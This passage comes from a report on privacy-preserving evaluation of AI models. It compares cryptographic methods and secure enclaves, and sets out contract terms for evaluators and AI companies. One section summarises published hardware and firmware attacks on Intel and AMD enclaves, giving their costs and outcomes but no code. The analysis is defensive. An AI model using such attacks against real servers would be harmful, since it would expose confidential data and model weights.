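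Some newer systems replace many of these messages with function secret sharing (FSS). The parties reveal only the sum of the hidden number and a random mask, and each uses a key prepared in advance to calculate its own share of the answer to a question such as "is the number below zero?". *FuseFSS* (Ma, Li and Schmid, 2026) handles all the non-linear steps that act on one number at a time with the same two FSS operations. It is 1.24 to 1.50 times as fast as SIGMA, the leading earlier design, and its keys are 20% to 24% smaller. It still needs new keys for every run.

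Homomorphic encryption cannot directly compute exponentials, divisions or comparisons, so the company has to replace each non-linear step with a polynomial, a formula made only of additions and multiplications. For example, 1 + x + x²/2 + x³/6 approximates the exponential function fairly well near zero. At x = 1 it gives 2.67 instead of 2.72, but at x = 5 it gives 39 instead of 148. A longer polynomial is more accurate but uses more of the multiplication budget, so it requires more bootstrapping. The hardest step in homomorphic encryption is LayerNorm's inverse square root. GELU, which requires the most communication in MPC, needs only a short polynomial.

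Hybrid systems use homomorphic encryption for the linear steps and MPC for the rest, but converting between the two adds substantial overhead. *EncFormer* (Zhu, Jin and colleagues, 2026) reduced this overhead and cut total time by a factor of 1.3 to 9.8 compared with earlier hybrids.

These substitutions matter to an evaluator because they can change the model. Of the 62 systems in the review, 40 run an approximation of the original model, 14 modify it, and only 7 reproduce it exactly. A score from an approximate version may not hold for the original. Before using it to judge the commercial model, the parties should run both versions openly on public questions and check that they give the same answers.

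### What protection against malicious parties adds

In the worked multiplication, the company could add 1 to its final share. The answer would then be 85, and the institute could not tell that it was wrong. A protocol designed for semi-honest parties, who follow the rules but try to learn what they can, has no defence against this. Of the 62 systems, 55 assume semi-honest parties, 4 protect against malicious ones and 3 are unclear.

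Protocols with malicious security make each party prove that its messages follow from the inputs it committed to at the start. If a proof fails, the honest party stops before accepting a result. The overhead depends on the calculation. *Two-Sided Malicious Security for Private Intersection-Sum with Cardinality* (Miao and Patel, 2020) presents such a protocol, which counts the entries two lists share and adds up the numbers attached to those entries. It sent four to five times as much data as the most efficient semi-honest version and cost 25 times as much to run in the cloud.

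*Private Transformer Inference in MLaaS* (2025), a survey, notes that some cheating leaves privacy intact. A party who refuses to send data stops the calculation, but the inputs can stay private. Wrong results are a bigger concern for an evaluator. Homomorphic encryption alone does not show that the company ran the right calculation, or even the right model. Zero-knowledge proofs, covered later, could provide that evidence. The threat model in Jayashankar and colleagues' paper excludes companies that return false results.

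### What a whole benchmark costs

*TRUCE* (Rajore, Chandran and colleagues, 2024) is an early comparison of ways to keep a benchmark private. Its open-source platform supports five designs. Three are among the simpler arrangements described earlier (API access, a public model that the benchmark's owner runs, and a trusted third party), and the other two are a secure enclave and MPC. The MPC option used SIGMA and gave each side a virtual machine with an Nvidia H100 graphics processor (GPU). A very fast connection of 24 gigabits per second linked the two machines.

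The researchers timed ten samples of each kind and reported the average. Multiplying their averages by the number of samples gives the time for a whole test:

| Model and test | Samples | Trusted third party | MPC | Data exchanged in MPC |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| BERT-Base, a small language model | 1,821 | 2.5 seconds | 40 minutes | 1.4 TB |
| VGG16, an image classifier | 10,000 | 5.5 seconds | 55 minutes | 3.2 TB |
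| Airavata, a Hindi language model | 5,010 | 42 seconds | 17 hours | 76 TB |
| Llama2-7B | 5,153 | 4.6 minutes | 18 hours | 199 TB |

For Llama2-7B, a language model with 7 billion weights, MPC took about 230 times as long as the ordinary calculation, while the enclave took about 1% longer. Eighteen hours is acceptable for a test run once. Transferring the 199 TB is harder, since it would take about 18 days over an ordinary one-gigabit connection. It would also cost around $16,000 at 8 cents per gigabyte, a typical price for sending data out of a cloud provider's network.

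Each language sample had only 100 tokens, and each timing covers a single pass through the model, which is enough to predict one more token. SIGMA's published times exclude preparing the keys and sending them to the parties. Das and colleagues put the keys at 255 to 419 GB for one pass through a model with 7 to 13 billion weights.

Homomorphic encryption has recently improved a great deal. In March 2025, Tlaie and Farrell judged it far from ready for modern language models (*Securing External Deeper-than-black-box GPAI Evaluations*). Jayashankar and colleagues then ran the first encrypted prefill, the stage in which a model reads the whole prompt and prepares its first output token, of Llama-3-8B, a model with 8 billion weights. It took 43 seconds. The encoded weights would have filled 112 TB of memory, so the researchers first had to compress them about a hundredfold.

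Fan, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *An Open-Source End-to-End FHE Implementation*, fitted the same model onto a single H100. You, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *TurboFHE*, report that a 128-token prompt took 94.5 seconds on one H100, 25.3 seconds on eight, and 21.6 seconds on eight RTX PRO 6000 GPUs, which are cheaper workstation cards. The single-GPU time is about 1,800 times the 0.053 seconds that Rajore and colleagues measured for Llama2-7B, but this ratio is only approximate because the models and prompts differ slightly.

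At these speeds, some tests are already practical. Suppose the institute has 1,000 multiple-choice questions of up to 128 tokens each and needs only the letter of the answer. Eight H100s, taking 25.3 seconds per question, would finish in about seven hours, and one H100 would need a little over a day.

Written replies are far more demanding, because a model generates them one token at a time. *CryptoGen* (2026) notes that most earlier private systems were designed for a single pass or a single next token, even when the model could generate text. Das and colleagues collected published costs for models with 7 to 13 billion weights and projected them to 70 billion:

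| System | Method and setting | Time per token, 7–13 billion weights | Data exchanged per token | Projected time per token, 70 billion weights |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SIGMA | MPC, two parties and a dealer, GPUs | 23–38 seconds, excluding preparation | 12–19 GB, plus keys | 115 seconds |
| PUMA | MPC, three parties, 20-gigabit network | 164 seconds | 2.1 GB | 27 minutes |
| BumbleBee | Hybrid, two parties, ordinary processors | 832 seconds | 5.6 GB | 2.3 hours |
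| NEXUS | Homomorphic encryption, four A100 GPUs | 52 seconds in batches of 32, or 28 minutes alone | Not listed | 7.6 minutes in batches, or 4 hours alone |

The rows are not a ranking, because the systems differ in hardware, security assumptions and what their figures include. The reviewers checked all 1,891 pairs among their 62 systems and found only one pair that was directly comparable. Figures can differ even for the same system. *From Models to Services* (2026), a review of security for hosted models, gives about five minutes per token for PUMA, whereas the 164 seconds above is the extra time for a second token, after the model has read the prompt.

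Suppose the same 1,000 questions need replies of 500 tokens each, or 500,000 tokens in total. At SIGMA's fastest speed of 23 seconds per token, one set of machines would need 133 days. At BumbleBee's speed, it would need 13 years. More machines would shorten the wait but wouldn't reduce the total work or the amount of data exchanged. SIGMA would exchange at least 6 million GB and need fresh keys for every token.

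The problem is worse for commercial models. An ordinary computer with suitable GPUs generates a token from a 70-billion-weight model in tens of milliseconds, and Das and colleagues estimate that the private methods have an overhead of 1,000 to 100,000 times. For a model of that size, SIGMA would need about 1.4 TB of keys for each pass. Sending them over a fast local network would take 20 minutes, ten times as long as the calculation.

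The largest dense model in the review that ran with full cryptographic protection had 13 billion weights, in a 2024 result. (A dense model uses all its weights for every token.) The largest public models have more than a trillion. The projections assume current methods, which can improve quickly, as recent progress with Llama-3-8B shows. But an institute that wants to test a frontier model on long written answers this year can't rely on cryptography alone.

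### Finding what two lists have in common

The same techniques take little computation when the question is small and fixed in advance. Private set intersection, for example, finds the overlap between two confidential lists. An evaluator could use it to check whether any of its secret questions appear word for word in a company's training data.

To compare their entries privately, the parties scramble them using secret keys, so that neither party could undo the scrambling alone. Using only a hash function, which turns each entry into a scrambled code, would not be enough because anyone can hash a guess. If the entries were phone numbers, the recipient could hash every possible phone number and look for matches.

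Ion, Kreuter and colleagues, in *On Deploying Secure Computing*, describe a version that Google had used for several years to measure advertising. One party knows who saw an advert, and the other knows who bought the product and how much they spent. They want to know how many people did both and how much those people spent in total. The protocol, which Google released as Private Join and Compute, works like this:

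1. The advertising company hashes each of its customer identifiers, raises the result to a secret power, shuffles the list and sends it to the shop.
2. The shop raises these numbers to its own secret power, shuffles them again and returns them. It also sends its own identifiers, hashed and raised to its secret power, with an encrypted purchase amount attached to each.
3. The advertising company raises the shop's identifiers to its own secret power. Every identifier from either list has now been through both powers, so the company can count the matches. It uses homomorphic encryption to add up the matching amounts without reading them.
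4. The shop, which holds the decryption key, decrypts the total.

Applying the two secret powers in either order gives the same result. Suppose an identifier hashes to 2 and the secret powers are 3 and 7. Modulo 101, 2³ = 8 and 8⁷ = 89. In the other order, 2⁷ = 27 and 27³ = 89. The real protocol uses numbers far too large for anyone to work backwards. Shuffling prevents the parties from learning which people matched.

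With 100,000 entries on each side, a run exchanged about 8 MB and cost 0.084 cents. Google typically did about 1,000 runs a day with each partner, which cost 84 cents. The designers chose semi-honest security because it was cheaper and because contracts and code audits could also deter cheating. Even if malicious security multiplied the cost by 25, as in Miao and Patel's experiment, a run would cost only about two cents.

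A contamination check would have limits that an advertising report does not have. The method finds only exact matches, so it would miss reworded questions, and the company could leave incriminating documents out of its list.

### Group error rates

xD, a technology team at the US Census Bureau, adapted this protocol to check whether a model works equally well for different groups. Suppose a government agency has built a model but has no data on its users' ethnicity, which the Census Bureau does have. xD's *Demonstrating privacy-preserving model auditing* (2025) explains the calculation. For each person, the agency records a 1 if the model was right and a 0 if it was wrong. The Bureau supplies a list of people in one demographic group. The protocol gives the number of people on both lists, N, and the sum of their 1s and 0s, K. The model's accuracy for that group is K/N, and its error rate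 is 1 − K/N.

In a small example from *Official Statistics for Responsible AI* (Lazovich, Walton and colleagues, 2024), the Bureau's group contains people 1, 2 and 3, and the agency has results for people 2, 3 and 901. Two people are on both lists, and the model was right about one of them, so its accuracy for the group is 50%.

xD repeated the protocol for each group. Ion and colleagues describe a cheaper variant in which one party divides its list into groups, and the other shuffles entries only within each group. This gives a separate total for every group at roughly the cost of a single run. Another variant stops if the overlap is too small. That would be a sensible addition here, since a "group" of one person would reveal whether the model was right about that individual.

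The demonstration used public data, and much of the engineering effort went into ordinary networking. According to xD's *Privacy-preserving model auditing demo* (2025), the government's cloud service could not handle the library's usual way of sending messages, so the team built a translator. The method also relies on the 1s and 0s being reported truthfully. An agency checking its own model has little reason to falsify them, but a company facing an outside audit might.

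### Judging whether another party's data is worth combining

Hospitals could often build better models by combining their records, but they can't tell in advance whether a particular partner's records will help. Xu found that for 10 of 12 hospitals, adding data from at least one of the others made models worse at predicting deaths in intensive care. A hospital would therefore like to compare datasets before negotiating to share them.

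Xu's method, Secure-KL, uses MPC to estimate how different two datasets are. It builds on Kullback–Leibler (KL) divergence, a standard measure of the difference between two probability distributions P and Q. KL divergence is the average of the logarithm of P(x)/Q(x) over records x drawn from P. If the distributions are identical, every ratio is 1 and the divergence is 0.

The hospitals don't know P and Q, so they train a simple model, a logistic regression, to predict which hospital a record came from. If both supply the same number of records and the model gives a record an 80% chance of coming from the first hospital, the estimated ratio is 0.8/0.2 = 4. If the model gives each hospital a 50% chance, the ratio is 1. The training and the comparison both run on hidden data, and the hospitals see only the final score.

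The scores matched those from readable data by over 90%. Xu then let each hospital combine its data with its three most promising partners, and compared Secure-KL with methods that reveal more. In the intensive-care data, Secure-KL chose better partners than comparing patient demographics or looking at a sample of 1% or 10% of a partner's records. In a second test, which predicted incomes from US survey data, all the methods performed about equally well.

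A low divergence shows that two datasets are similar, but similar data isn't always useful. Xu found that the method's success depended on how closely similarity and usefulness were related for a given hospital. If the model owner already has a model and a test set, another of Xu's methods estimates more directly how much new data would improve that model. In a trial with 100 datasets, its private ranking had a 92.3% correlation with the true ranking when the categories were deliberately unbalanced, and 96.0% when the datasets instead contained deliberately wrong labels.

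## Using a secure enclave as the neutral computer

A secure enclave, also called a trusted execution environment (TEE), can run a model at almost normal speed because the processor calculates with readable numbers and encrypts them only when they leave the chip. The enclaves that matter most for AI use Intel's TDX or AMD's SEV-SNP. Each protects a whole virtual machine, a simulated computer that shares a physical server with others. The hypervisor, the program that manages virtual machines, can normally read everything inside them, but TDX and SEV-SNP are meant to keep it out. This lets the company and the institute put their secrets on one machine, but they have to trust the chip and anyone who can physically reach it.

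### How an enclave shows what it is running

Trask and colleagues explain how the protection works:

1. The manufacturer burns secret numbers into each chip. The chip derives a private signing key from them, and the manufacturer publishes a certificate for the matching public key.
2. Whenever an enclave starts, the chip creates a new key and uses it to encrypt the enclave's memory. Software can't read this key, and the chip destroys it when the enclave stops. A program inside the enclave encrypts the disk with separate keys.
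3. Each layer of software measures the next one before starting it, from the firmware and the operating system up to the evaluation program. Measuring a file means calculating its hash, which changes completely if anyone alters a single character.
4. The enclave creates another pair of keys for receiving secrets.
5. A party sends the enclave a nonce, a random number that it will never use again. The chip signs an attestation report containing the measurements, the enclave's public key and the nonce.
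6. The party checks that the signature leads back to the manufacturer's certificate, that the nonce is its own, and that the measurements match the agreed software. If everything matches, it sends its secrets over a channel secured with the enclave's key.

Systems commonly combine the measurements by keeping a running value, M. For each new layer L, the system replaces M with H(M, H(L)), where H is the hash function. Software can add to this value but can't reset it, so a malicious layer can't erase the record of its own loading.

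The nonce prevents the host from reusing a report made before it changed the software. The certificate prevents anyone from forging a report on an ordinary computer. A party should also check the settings in the report, because the host can read the memory of an enclave that is in debug mode.

The key in the report is meant to stop the host from showing a party one machine's report and then collecting that party's secrets on another, but this is difficult to get right. SC Media's *Confidential computing's remote attestation protocol may have fundamental flaw* (2026) describes research led by Muhammad Usama Sardar of TU Dresden, which tested seven ways of tying a report to a connection. With all seven, an attacker could let a user check a genuine server and then divert the user's data to a malicious one, because a report identifies a server's software but not its location. The weakness affected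 real products, including the system Meta uses for private AI processing in WhatsApp.

The parties also can't inspect the chip's lowest layers, its microcode and security firmware, because the manufacturers keep the source code secret. But the parties can refuse old versions. The signing key depends on the firmware version, so a chip with outdated firmware should not be able to sign as if it were up to date.

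### Why the software has to be reproducible

With the hash function that AMD uses, a measurement is a string of 96 letters and digits. If the institute receives the same string twice, it knows that the enclave ran the same software both times, but not what that software does. To find that out, it needs to know which source code produces the string.

A reproducible build solves this problem. It turns the same public source code into exactly the same file on anyone's computer, whereas ordinary builds often differ because they include details such as the date. The institute, or an auditor it chooses, can read the source code, build the program, calculate the measurement and compare it with the one in the report. Every honest person who rebuilds the program should get the same result, so one person who publishes a mismatch can expose a substitution.

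The Gemini tests fell short of this standard. Google publishes the source code and expected measurements for the operating system it used, and outsiders have validated the build process. But each build needs Google's private signing keys, so nobody else can reproduce it. Google's own service also signed and verified the attestation report. Trask and colleagues acknowledge that this required more trust in Google.

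*Physical integrity, attestation, and the state of permissionless TEEs*, an essay by an engineer at the blockchain company Ritual, finds similar gaps at all three large cloud providers:

- Google signs and publishes the firmware that starts its confidential virtual machines, but not the source code. The host also supplies tables describing the hardware, which can contain code that the virtual machine runs, and Google publishes no signed measurements for them.
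- Microsoft has published the source code of the layer it places beneath a customer's system, but customers can't confirm that the running copy matches it.
- Amazon's Nitro enclaves don't encrypt memory at all, and Amazon vouches for them itself.

The essay concludes that customers of any of the three still have to trust the operator.

Even a reproducible program can be unsafe. *AMD SEV-SNP* (2026), an introduction to AMD's technology, stresses that attestation shows which code the enclave loaded but not whether that code is correct. For example, if the approved operating system allows remote logins, an administrator could log in after both parties have checked the attestation report and change the evaluation program. Enclave software therefore needs to leave out remote login and restrict what programs can send out.

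### From one customer to two

Cloud customers normally use an enclave to protect their data from the cloud provider. The company and the institute can use the same features to protect their data from each other, as long as neither can change the software once it is running. They agree on a program, and one of them rents the enclave. Each sends its own nonce and checks the report itself. Once both have approved the computation, they upload the weights and the questions. The program releases the result to whoever the parties have chosen, and the enclave shuts down.

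Both parties have to check the report. If the institute accepted the company's word that the measurements matched, the company could run a different program that copied the questions. Both also have to approve the specific computation, because the agreed software might be able to run many different computations. In the Gemini tests, PySyft ran code only after both sides had approved it. A later section explains what the parties can do if some of that code is secret.

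The party that rents the enclave can switch it off. If the company rented it and could watch the scores come in, it could stop a test that was going badly and blame a technical fault. To prevent this, either the program should release nothing until the test is finished, or the institute should rent the enclave.

### Adding a GPU

An enclave on an ordinary processor (CPU) does not automatically cover the GPU, which does most of a language model's work and has its own memory. Nvidia's H100 GPU can extend the protection because it can produce its own signed reports. Software in the CPU enclave checks the GPU's report and sets up an encrypted connection before sending the weights and prompts to the GPU. The agreed program has to include this check and stop if it fails. The Gemini test with AVERI used a Google Cloud virtual machine with Intel TDX, a single H100 with 80 GB of memory, and Nvidia's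 attestation software.

Trask and colleagues put the slowdown at less than 5%, a figure they take from a 2023 post on the technical blog of Nvidia, which sells the chip. Their paper doesn't report a slowdown for Gemini, or give the model, prompt length or number of GPUs behind Nvidia's figure.

The figure is plausible for this kind of test. Much of the extra work is encrypting data that moves between the CPU and the GPU, so the slowdown should be small for a model that loads its weights once and then answers short prompts, and larger for a task that constantly moves large amounts of data. Rajore and colleagues measured a 1% slowdown, which is consistent with this, though their test covered only a single pass through the model. Even a 25% slowdown would lengthen a one-hour test by only 15 minutes, so the exact figure hardly affects the choice between an enclave and MPC.

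### Physical attacks

Chip makers promise less protection than Trask and colleagues, who argue that the cloud provider and the chip maker would have to collude to break an enclave's guarantees, provided that the chip's secrets never leak. That would make enclaves very safe, since the two are usually separate companies with a lot to lose. According to *AMD SEV-SNP*, however, AMD's design protects against a cloud company that misuses its control of the hypervisor, but relies on that company to keep the physical machine secure.

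Four recent attacks exploited that trust. In each, researchers placed a small circuit board, called an interposer, between a server's processor and its memory.

| Attack | Equipment cost | Systems affected | What the researchers obtained |
|---|---|---|---|
| WireTap (2025) | Under $1,000 | Intel SGX with DDR4 memory | The key that signs attestation reports |
| Battering RAM (2025) | Under €50 | Intel SGX and AMD SEV-SNP with DDR4 memory | The ability to read and change memory protected by SGX |
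| TEE.fail (2025) | Under $1,000 | Intel SGX, Intel TDX and AMD SEV-SNP with DDR5 memory | Intel keys for forging reports, and secret keys from a program in an AMD enclave |
| DDRop (2026) | $159 | Intel SGX, Intel TDX and AMD SEV-SNP with DDR5 memory | On TDX, access to protected memory and forged reports |

SGX is an older Intel technology that usually protects a single program instead of a whole virtual machine. Intel plans to phase it out in favour of TDX, according to Tom's Hardware's *Intel to phase out SGX after Xeon Diamond Rapids*. DDR5 is the newer generation of memory, so TEE.fail and DDRop matter most for new AI servers.

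The attacks take little time. *Physical integrity* puts WireTap at under 45 minutes and TEE.fail at about 15, while Schneier (2025), in *New Attacks Against Secure Enclaves*, describes TEE.fail as a three-minute attack. TEE.fail also requires control of the operating system's core, which a cloud provider has on its own servers. De Meulemeester, Gloor and colleagues (2026), in *DDRop*, needed only one brief visit to install the board and could do everything else with software. They note that a technician could make that visit, or that someone could plant the board before the server is delivered. Renting a machine for only a few hours therefore does not protect the user if someone has already tampered with it.

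A forged report is especially dangerous for an evaluator. The WireTap researchers told The Hacker News (2025) that they took their key from a machine that still had Intel's fully trusted status. With such a key, a dishonest host could run an ordinary, unprotected computer and send the institute a report that passes every check. The institute would then upload its questions to a machine the host can read.

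Confidential GPUs don't solve this problem. In *TEE.fail*, Chuang, Seto and colleagues presented a GPU report from a different computer as their own, then ran AI software without any enclave protection.

These weaknesses arise partly because enclaves were designed for large amounts of memory. *TEE Anchor* (2026) traces both TEE.fail and Battering RAM to encryption that always turns the same data at the same memory address into the same scrambled text, as long as the key stays the same, so somebody watching the memory can recognise repeated values. Intel's earlier enclaves for personal computers avoided this but supported only 512 MB of encrypted memory, compared with 1 TB on servers. A model with one billion weights normally takes up about 2 GB, so the older design is of little use for language models. DDRop instead exploits the processor's inability to check whether the data it reads from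 memory is the latest version.

The manufacturers have declined to treat the 2025 attacks as faults. Intel (2025) responded to WireTap and Battering RAM by saying that such attacks were outside the protection it offered, and repeated this in *TEE.fail* (2025). AMD says in *Compromising Trusted Execution Environments through DDR5 Memory Bus Interposition* (2025) that it plans no mitigations. Chuang and colleagues report that Intel can't fix the memory encryption on existing chips with an update.

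Intel recommends a stronger integrity setting against attacks like Battering RAM. But De Meulemeester and colleagues found that an attacker could still use DDRop to forge the report of a virtual machine that the attacker had started.

Intel also advises customers to find out how well a machine's owner protects it physically. A large cloud provider's data centre has guards, identity checks and cameras, so an outsider would struggle to install anything. These measures are less effective against the provider's own staff, and a server room owned by one party gives the other very little protection.

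The parties can ask for evidence of where the machine is. Chuang and colleagues suggest accepting reports only from particular chips known to be in secure buildings. Intel has designed a way for the organisation that controls a machine to sign a statement identifying it, but *Physical integrity* reports that the tools are not yet available and that AMD has announced nothing similar. Some cloud services already provide their own signatures. For example, Confidential Space, used for the Gemini tests, issues statements signed by Google.

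### Attacks that need only software

In April 2026, ETH Zurich researchers disclosed Fabricked, an attack that also broke AMD's protection, but without physical access to the server. Tom's Hardware reports that it lets a malicious host read and change the memory of confidential virtual machines and forge their reports, and that it worked every time.

In May, *Insecure Despite Proven Updated* (2026) showed how to extract the secret from which AMD's EPYC Milan server chips derive their signing keys. Anyone with this secret could in principle sign a report showing fully updated firmware, so checking the version number gives little assurance on a compromised Milan chip.

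Two more attacks became public in November. According to The Hacker News' *New Mior and Skyfall Attacks Let Rogue Cloud Hosts Steal Secrets* (2026), Mior let the host read and change protected memory in all 1,000 attempts. In a separate test, the researchers made a malicious virtual machine's report describe harmless software. Skyfall recovered a disk-encryption key from a test machine. Both attacks require control of the hypervisor, and Mior also requires control of the server's startup firmware and a device such as a graphics card. A cloud provider could control all three.

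AMD lists fixes for both attacks dated August 2026, but it planned to give server makers the wider firmware updates in November for Skyfall and December for Mior. An AMD server rented in early December may therefore still lack some of the protection. The parties should ask which updates the host has installed and reject reports that show older firmware versions. Mior's designers tested it only on a recent Zen 5 chip, but they think the two previous generations may also be vulnerable.

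These particular AMD flaws don't apply to the Gemini test with AVERI, which used Intel TDX. However, TEE.fail and DDRop affect TDX.

An enclave can also leak information through its pattern of memory use, even when the contents of its memory stay hidden. AMD's *TDXRay* describes a tool that lets a host trace which parts of memory an Intel TDX machine uses. If a program uses different parts of memory for different questions, the trace could reveal something about those questions. AMD also considers such leaks outside SEV-SNP's protection and advises developers to write programs whose behaviour does not depend on secret data.

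### What remains of the collusion argument

A host can break an enclave without the chip maker's help by tampering with the hardware or exploiting an unpatched software flaw, so the collusion argument is too strong. A cloud company controls its own servers, which is enough to let it tamper with the hardware.

A government might also be able to force both the cloud provider and the chip maker to help. *Physical integrity* argues that orders to both could defeat an enclave, although it admits to speculating that chip makers keep the necessary keys. Its main example is the US national security letter, a demand for records that comes with a gag order. The example is weak because letters to communications companies cover only records such as subscriber and billing details. But Google, Microsoft, Amazon, Intel and AMD are all American, so an institute in another country that wants to keep its questions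 from the US government should not assume that the cloud provider and the chip maker are independent.

Even so, an enclave can greatly reduce the risk that questions accidentally end up in training data, because a well-designed one keeps the readable questions out of the company's logs. A deliberate attack, such as installing an interposer, would require people to tamper with a server or its software, which creates evidence and potential whistleblowers. Researchers demonstrated these attacks in laboratories, which shows that a determined host could carry them out but not that cloud companies are doing so.

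Experts still see enclaves as important for AI security. Gekker, Steratore and colleagues (2026) consulted more than 20 leaders and specialists from industry, government and research for *AI Security Priorities*. The paper ranks wider use of confidential computing, the general name for this technology, fourth among priorities for protecting AI systems.

### How the trust compares with MPC

In MPC, the company's computer holds only random-looking shares of the institute's questions. The company, its cloud provider and its chipmaker could not read the questions from those shares even if they worked together. The institute has to trust its own computer, the cryptography, the software that implements it and the dealer, if there is one.

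An enclave handles the weights and the questions in readable form on one chip, so a successful attack could expose both, and the parties might never find out. The institute has to trust the chip maker, the host's physical security, the firmware and whoever verifies the report.

A sound attestation report from an enclave provides evidence of which program ran, whereas most MPC systems for language models assume that both parties follow the protocol. Neither method shows that the company supplied the right weights. Enclaves are much faster than MPC, as the earlier comparison showed.

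The parties can combine enclaves with MPC by running each side of the protocol in a separate enclave with a different host. An attacker would then have to break both enclaves to read the secrets, but the calculation would be as slow as ordinary MPC. Copying both secrets to several enclaves would make the secrets less safe, because each additional host could leak them. The copies would only help the parties check the answer, since a host that changed the calculation would get a different result from the others.

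Between an enclave and cryptography, only the enclave is currently practical for long written answers from a large model. Cryptography may be worth the extra hours if the questions are irreplaceable and the institute needs only short answers from a smaller model.

### Questions to ask before uploading anything

Each party should answer these questions separately, since an arrangement that is safe for the company may not be safe for the institute.

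| Question | Why it matters | What to ask for |
|---|---|---|
| Who owns the building? | Anyone who can reach the server may be able to add hardware that defeats its encryption. | A professional data centre that neither party controls, and signed evidence that the machine is there |
| Who runs the host? | The host controls the hypervisor and decides when to install security updates. | A list of installed updates, and a minimum firmware version that both parties enforce |
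| Who verifies the report? | A dishonest verifier could approve the wrong software. | Reproducible software, and a separate check by each party |
| Which of them gains from cheating? | An enclave offers less protection against a host that wants the secrets. | A different host, or MPC if the calculation is small enough |

The protection an enclave offers depends partly on what the organisations that control the building, the host and the verification would gain by attacking it. A cloud company with no interest in the model's score has little reason to attack, and its reputation would suffer badly if anyone found out. A rival AI company would gain much more from obtaining the weights, as would the model owner from seeing the questions. If one of these two controls the building, the host and the verification, the other party should treat the enclave mainly as protection against accidents.

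## Settling roles, contracts and legal duties

Before they install any software, the institute and the company should agree in writing on who may start a test, who sees the score, and who pays if the questions leak. Neither an enclave nor a cryptographic protocol settles these points. Agreement becomes much harder once a score exists, because each side then knows which terms would favour it.

### Six decisions to write down

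| Decision | A reasonable starting point for the biology benchmark |
|---|---|
| Who hosts and who pays? | A data centre that neither side controls. The institute rents the machine, and each side pays its own staff. |
| Who may veto? | Either side may refuse a computation before it starts. Neither may stop it or withhold the score afterwards. |
| Who receives the answer? | Both sides, at the same time. |
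| Who may publish it? | The institute, after a fixed period in which the company can request redactions from an agreed list. |
| Who is liable for a leak? | Each side, for anything that escapes through its own staff, systems or contractors. |
| How do disputes end? | A named technical expert decides questions of fact, and an arbitrator decides the rest. |

Payment affects how far outsiders will believe the result. Anthropic's *An update on independent evaluators* (2026) lists independence among its requirements for evaluators, and rules out those who hold equity in the company or depend on it financially. The nonprofit evaluation group METR took no money from Anthropic for a large assessment in autumn 2026 but accepted free use of the company's models, according to Bot Mutiny's *METR Estimates Anthropic Is Improving Its Models About Twice as Fast* (2026). The parties can deal with a benefit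 this modest by disclosing it.

"Veto" can mean refusing to run a test or refusing to publish its result, and a contract should treat these separately. A company that can block publication after seeing the score can ensure that only good scores appear.

Most disputes will be about facts that few people can check, such as whether the enclave ran the approved program. A lawsuit could force both sides to show their secrets to lawyers and judges, whereas an expert both sides accept could rerun the same software on public questions. The contract should also say that if the two sides can't agree, nothing runs, each keeps its own material, and either may say publicly that no test took place. Without that last right, a company could refuse an evaluation and nobody outside would know.

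### Matching the terms to the risks

A taskforce at the Royal United Services Institute (RUSI), a British defence think tank, has produced a useful checklist for such contracts in *Developing a Framework for Secure Third-Party Access to Frontier AI* (Hurel, Glantz and Cuthbert, 2026). The taskforce drew on 39 experts, mostly through three online workshops in late 2025. Google supported the work, and staff from AI companies took part. The paper covers only closed models and leaves out access by regulators and the police.

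The framework has seven categories of risk:

- **Model theft:** someone gets a working copy, either by taking the weights or by training another model on the original's answers (distillation).
- **Capability reconstruction:** someone learns enough about the training to build a similar model.
- **Model manipulation:** someone alters the model, for example by adding a hidden backdoor.
- **Jailbreak or safety bypass:** someone gets round the model's safeguards.
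- **Accidental exposure:** someone reveals sensitive material by mistake.
- **Credential compromise:** someone steals an evaluator's login.
- **Access persistence:** access stays open after the evaluation ends.

It adds weaponisation, the use of a model to cause real harm, as a possible outcome of the others.

A matrix then rates these risks for each type of access. The report's summary counts six types and its main text seven, while the matrix has eight rows: queries, reading the model's internals, changing them, configuration, training data, evaluation data, connected tools, and computing infrastructure. The row for queries, the access an evaluator needs for almost any test, reads as follows:

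| Risk | Rating | How it could happen |
|---|---|---|
| Model theft | Medium | Distillation through systematic queries, or misuse of the API to copy the model |
| Capability reconstruction | Low | Probing to map the model's abilities or identify it by its behaviour |
| Model manipulation | Not applicable | – |
| Jailbreak or safety bypass | High | Exploiting patterns in refusals, conflicts between the model's goals, and gaps in its safety training |
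| Weaponisation | Medium | Spreading jailbreaks or documents about dangerous abilities |
| Accidental exposure | Low | Unintended disclosure of weaknesses in the safeguards |
| Credential compromise | Medium | Evaluators' logins leaking, or evaluators sharing or storing them carelessly |
| Access persistence | Medium | Extracting information over a long period, or using the API beyond the approved scope |

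"High" means an attack would be much harder without this access, "medium" means the access helps substantially, and "low" means it contributes only indirectly. The ratings are expert judgements, which Hurel and colleagues call indicative.

A joint analysis that releases only a score would remove much of the theft risk in this row, because the evaluator would have no replies from the model to train a copy on. An evaluator that reads the replies, as AVERI's staff did in the Gemini test, could still train a copy on them.

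The framework also divides safeguards into technical, procedural and contractual controls. The technical controls against stolen logins, for example, include hardware security keys, the procedural ones include staff training, and the contractual ones include a security assessment of the evaluator before it gets access. The developer is responsible for every technical control, and both sides share responsibility for every contractual one. The table of controls has no row for model manipulation, even though the report rates permission to change a model's internals as the riskiest kind of access.

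The seven categories describe harm to the developer, and none covers a company reading an evaluator's secret questions or training on them. This is a bigger gap for a joint analysis. The institute therefore needs to add its own clauses, such as a ban on logging prompts and a duty to delete any prompts that staff find.

Both sides have reason to worry about leaks. In February 2023, Meta gave its LLaMA model to approved researchers, and the full weights soon appeared on the file-sharing network BitTorrent. Attackers also target evaluators. METR (2026) reports that attackers stole one of its API keys in March 2026, and in May tried to reach internal data through a connection METR had exposed by mistake. METR believes the attackers got no sensitive information, but it treated both incidents as near misses.

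Liability is hard to enforce when nobody can tell where a leak began. If the institute's questions turn up in a training set two years later, the company can suggest that the institute leaked them. Penalties therefore work better when they attach to observable events, such as reporting a breach late, keeping an expired account open or failing to delete files. Hurel and colleagues recommend terms on all three. They also suggest requiring evaluators to report dangerous abilities to the developer within a set number of hours, and legally protecting evaluators who act in good faith.

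### Who can refuse an analysis

The terms matter only if the analysis goes ahead, and that depends on who has the power to say no.

| Option | Who can refuse | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Voluntary agreement with mutual veto | Either side, for any reason | The Gemini tests |
| Neutral host | Either side, by not submitting its material | NIST's AITE programme |
| Confidential reviewer with a redacted report | The company, which admits the reviewer and can remove evidence from the report | METR's work at Anthropic |
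| Access required by law | The company, but only on legal grounds | Data requests under the EU's Digital Services Act |

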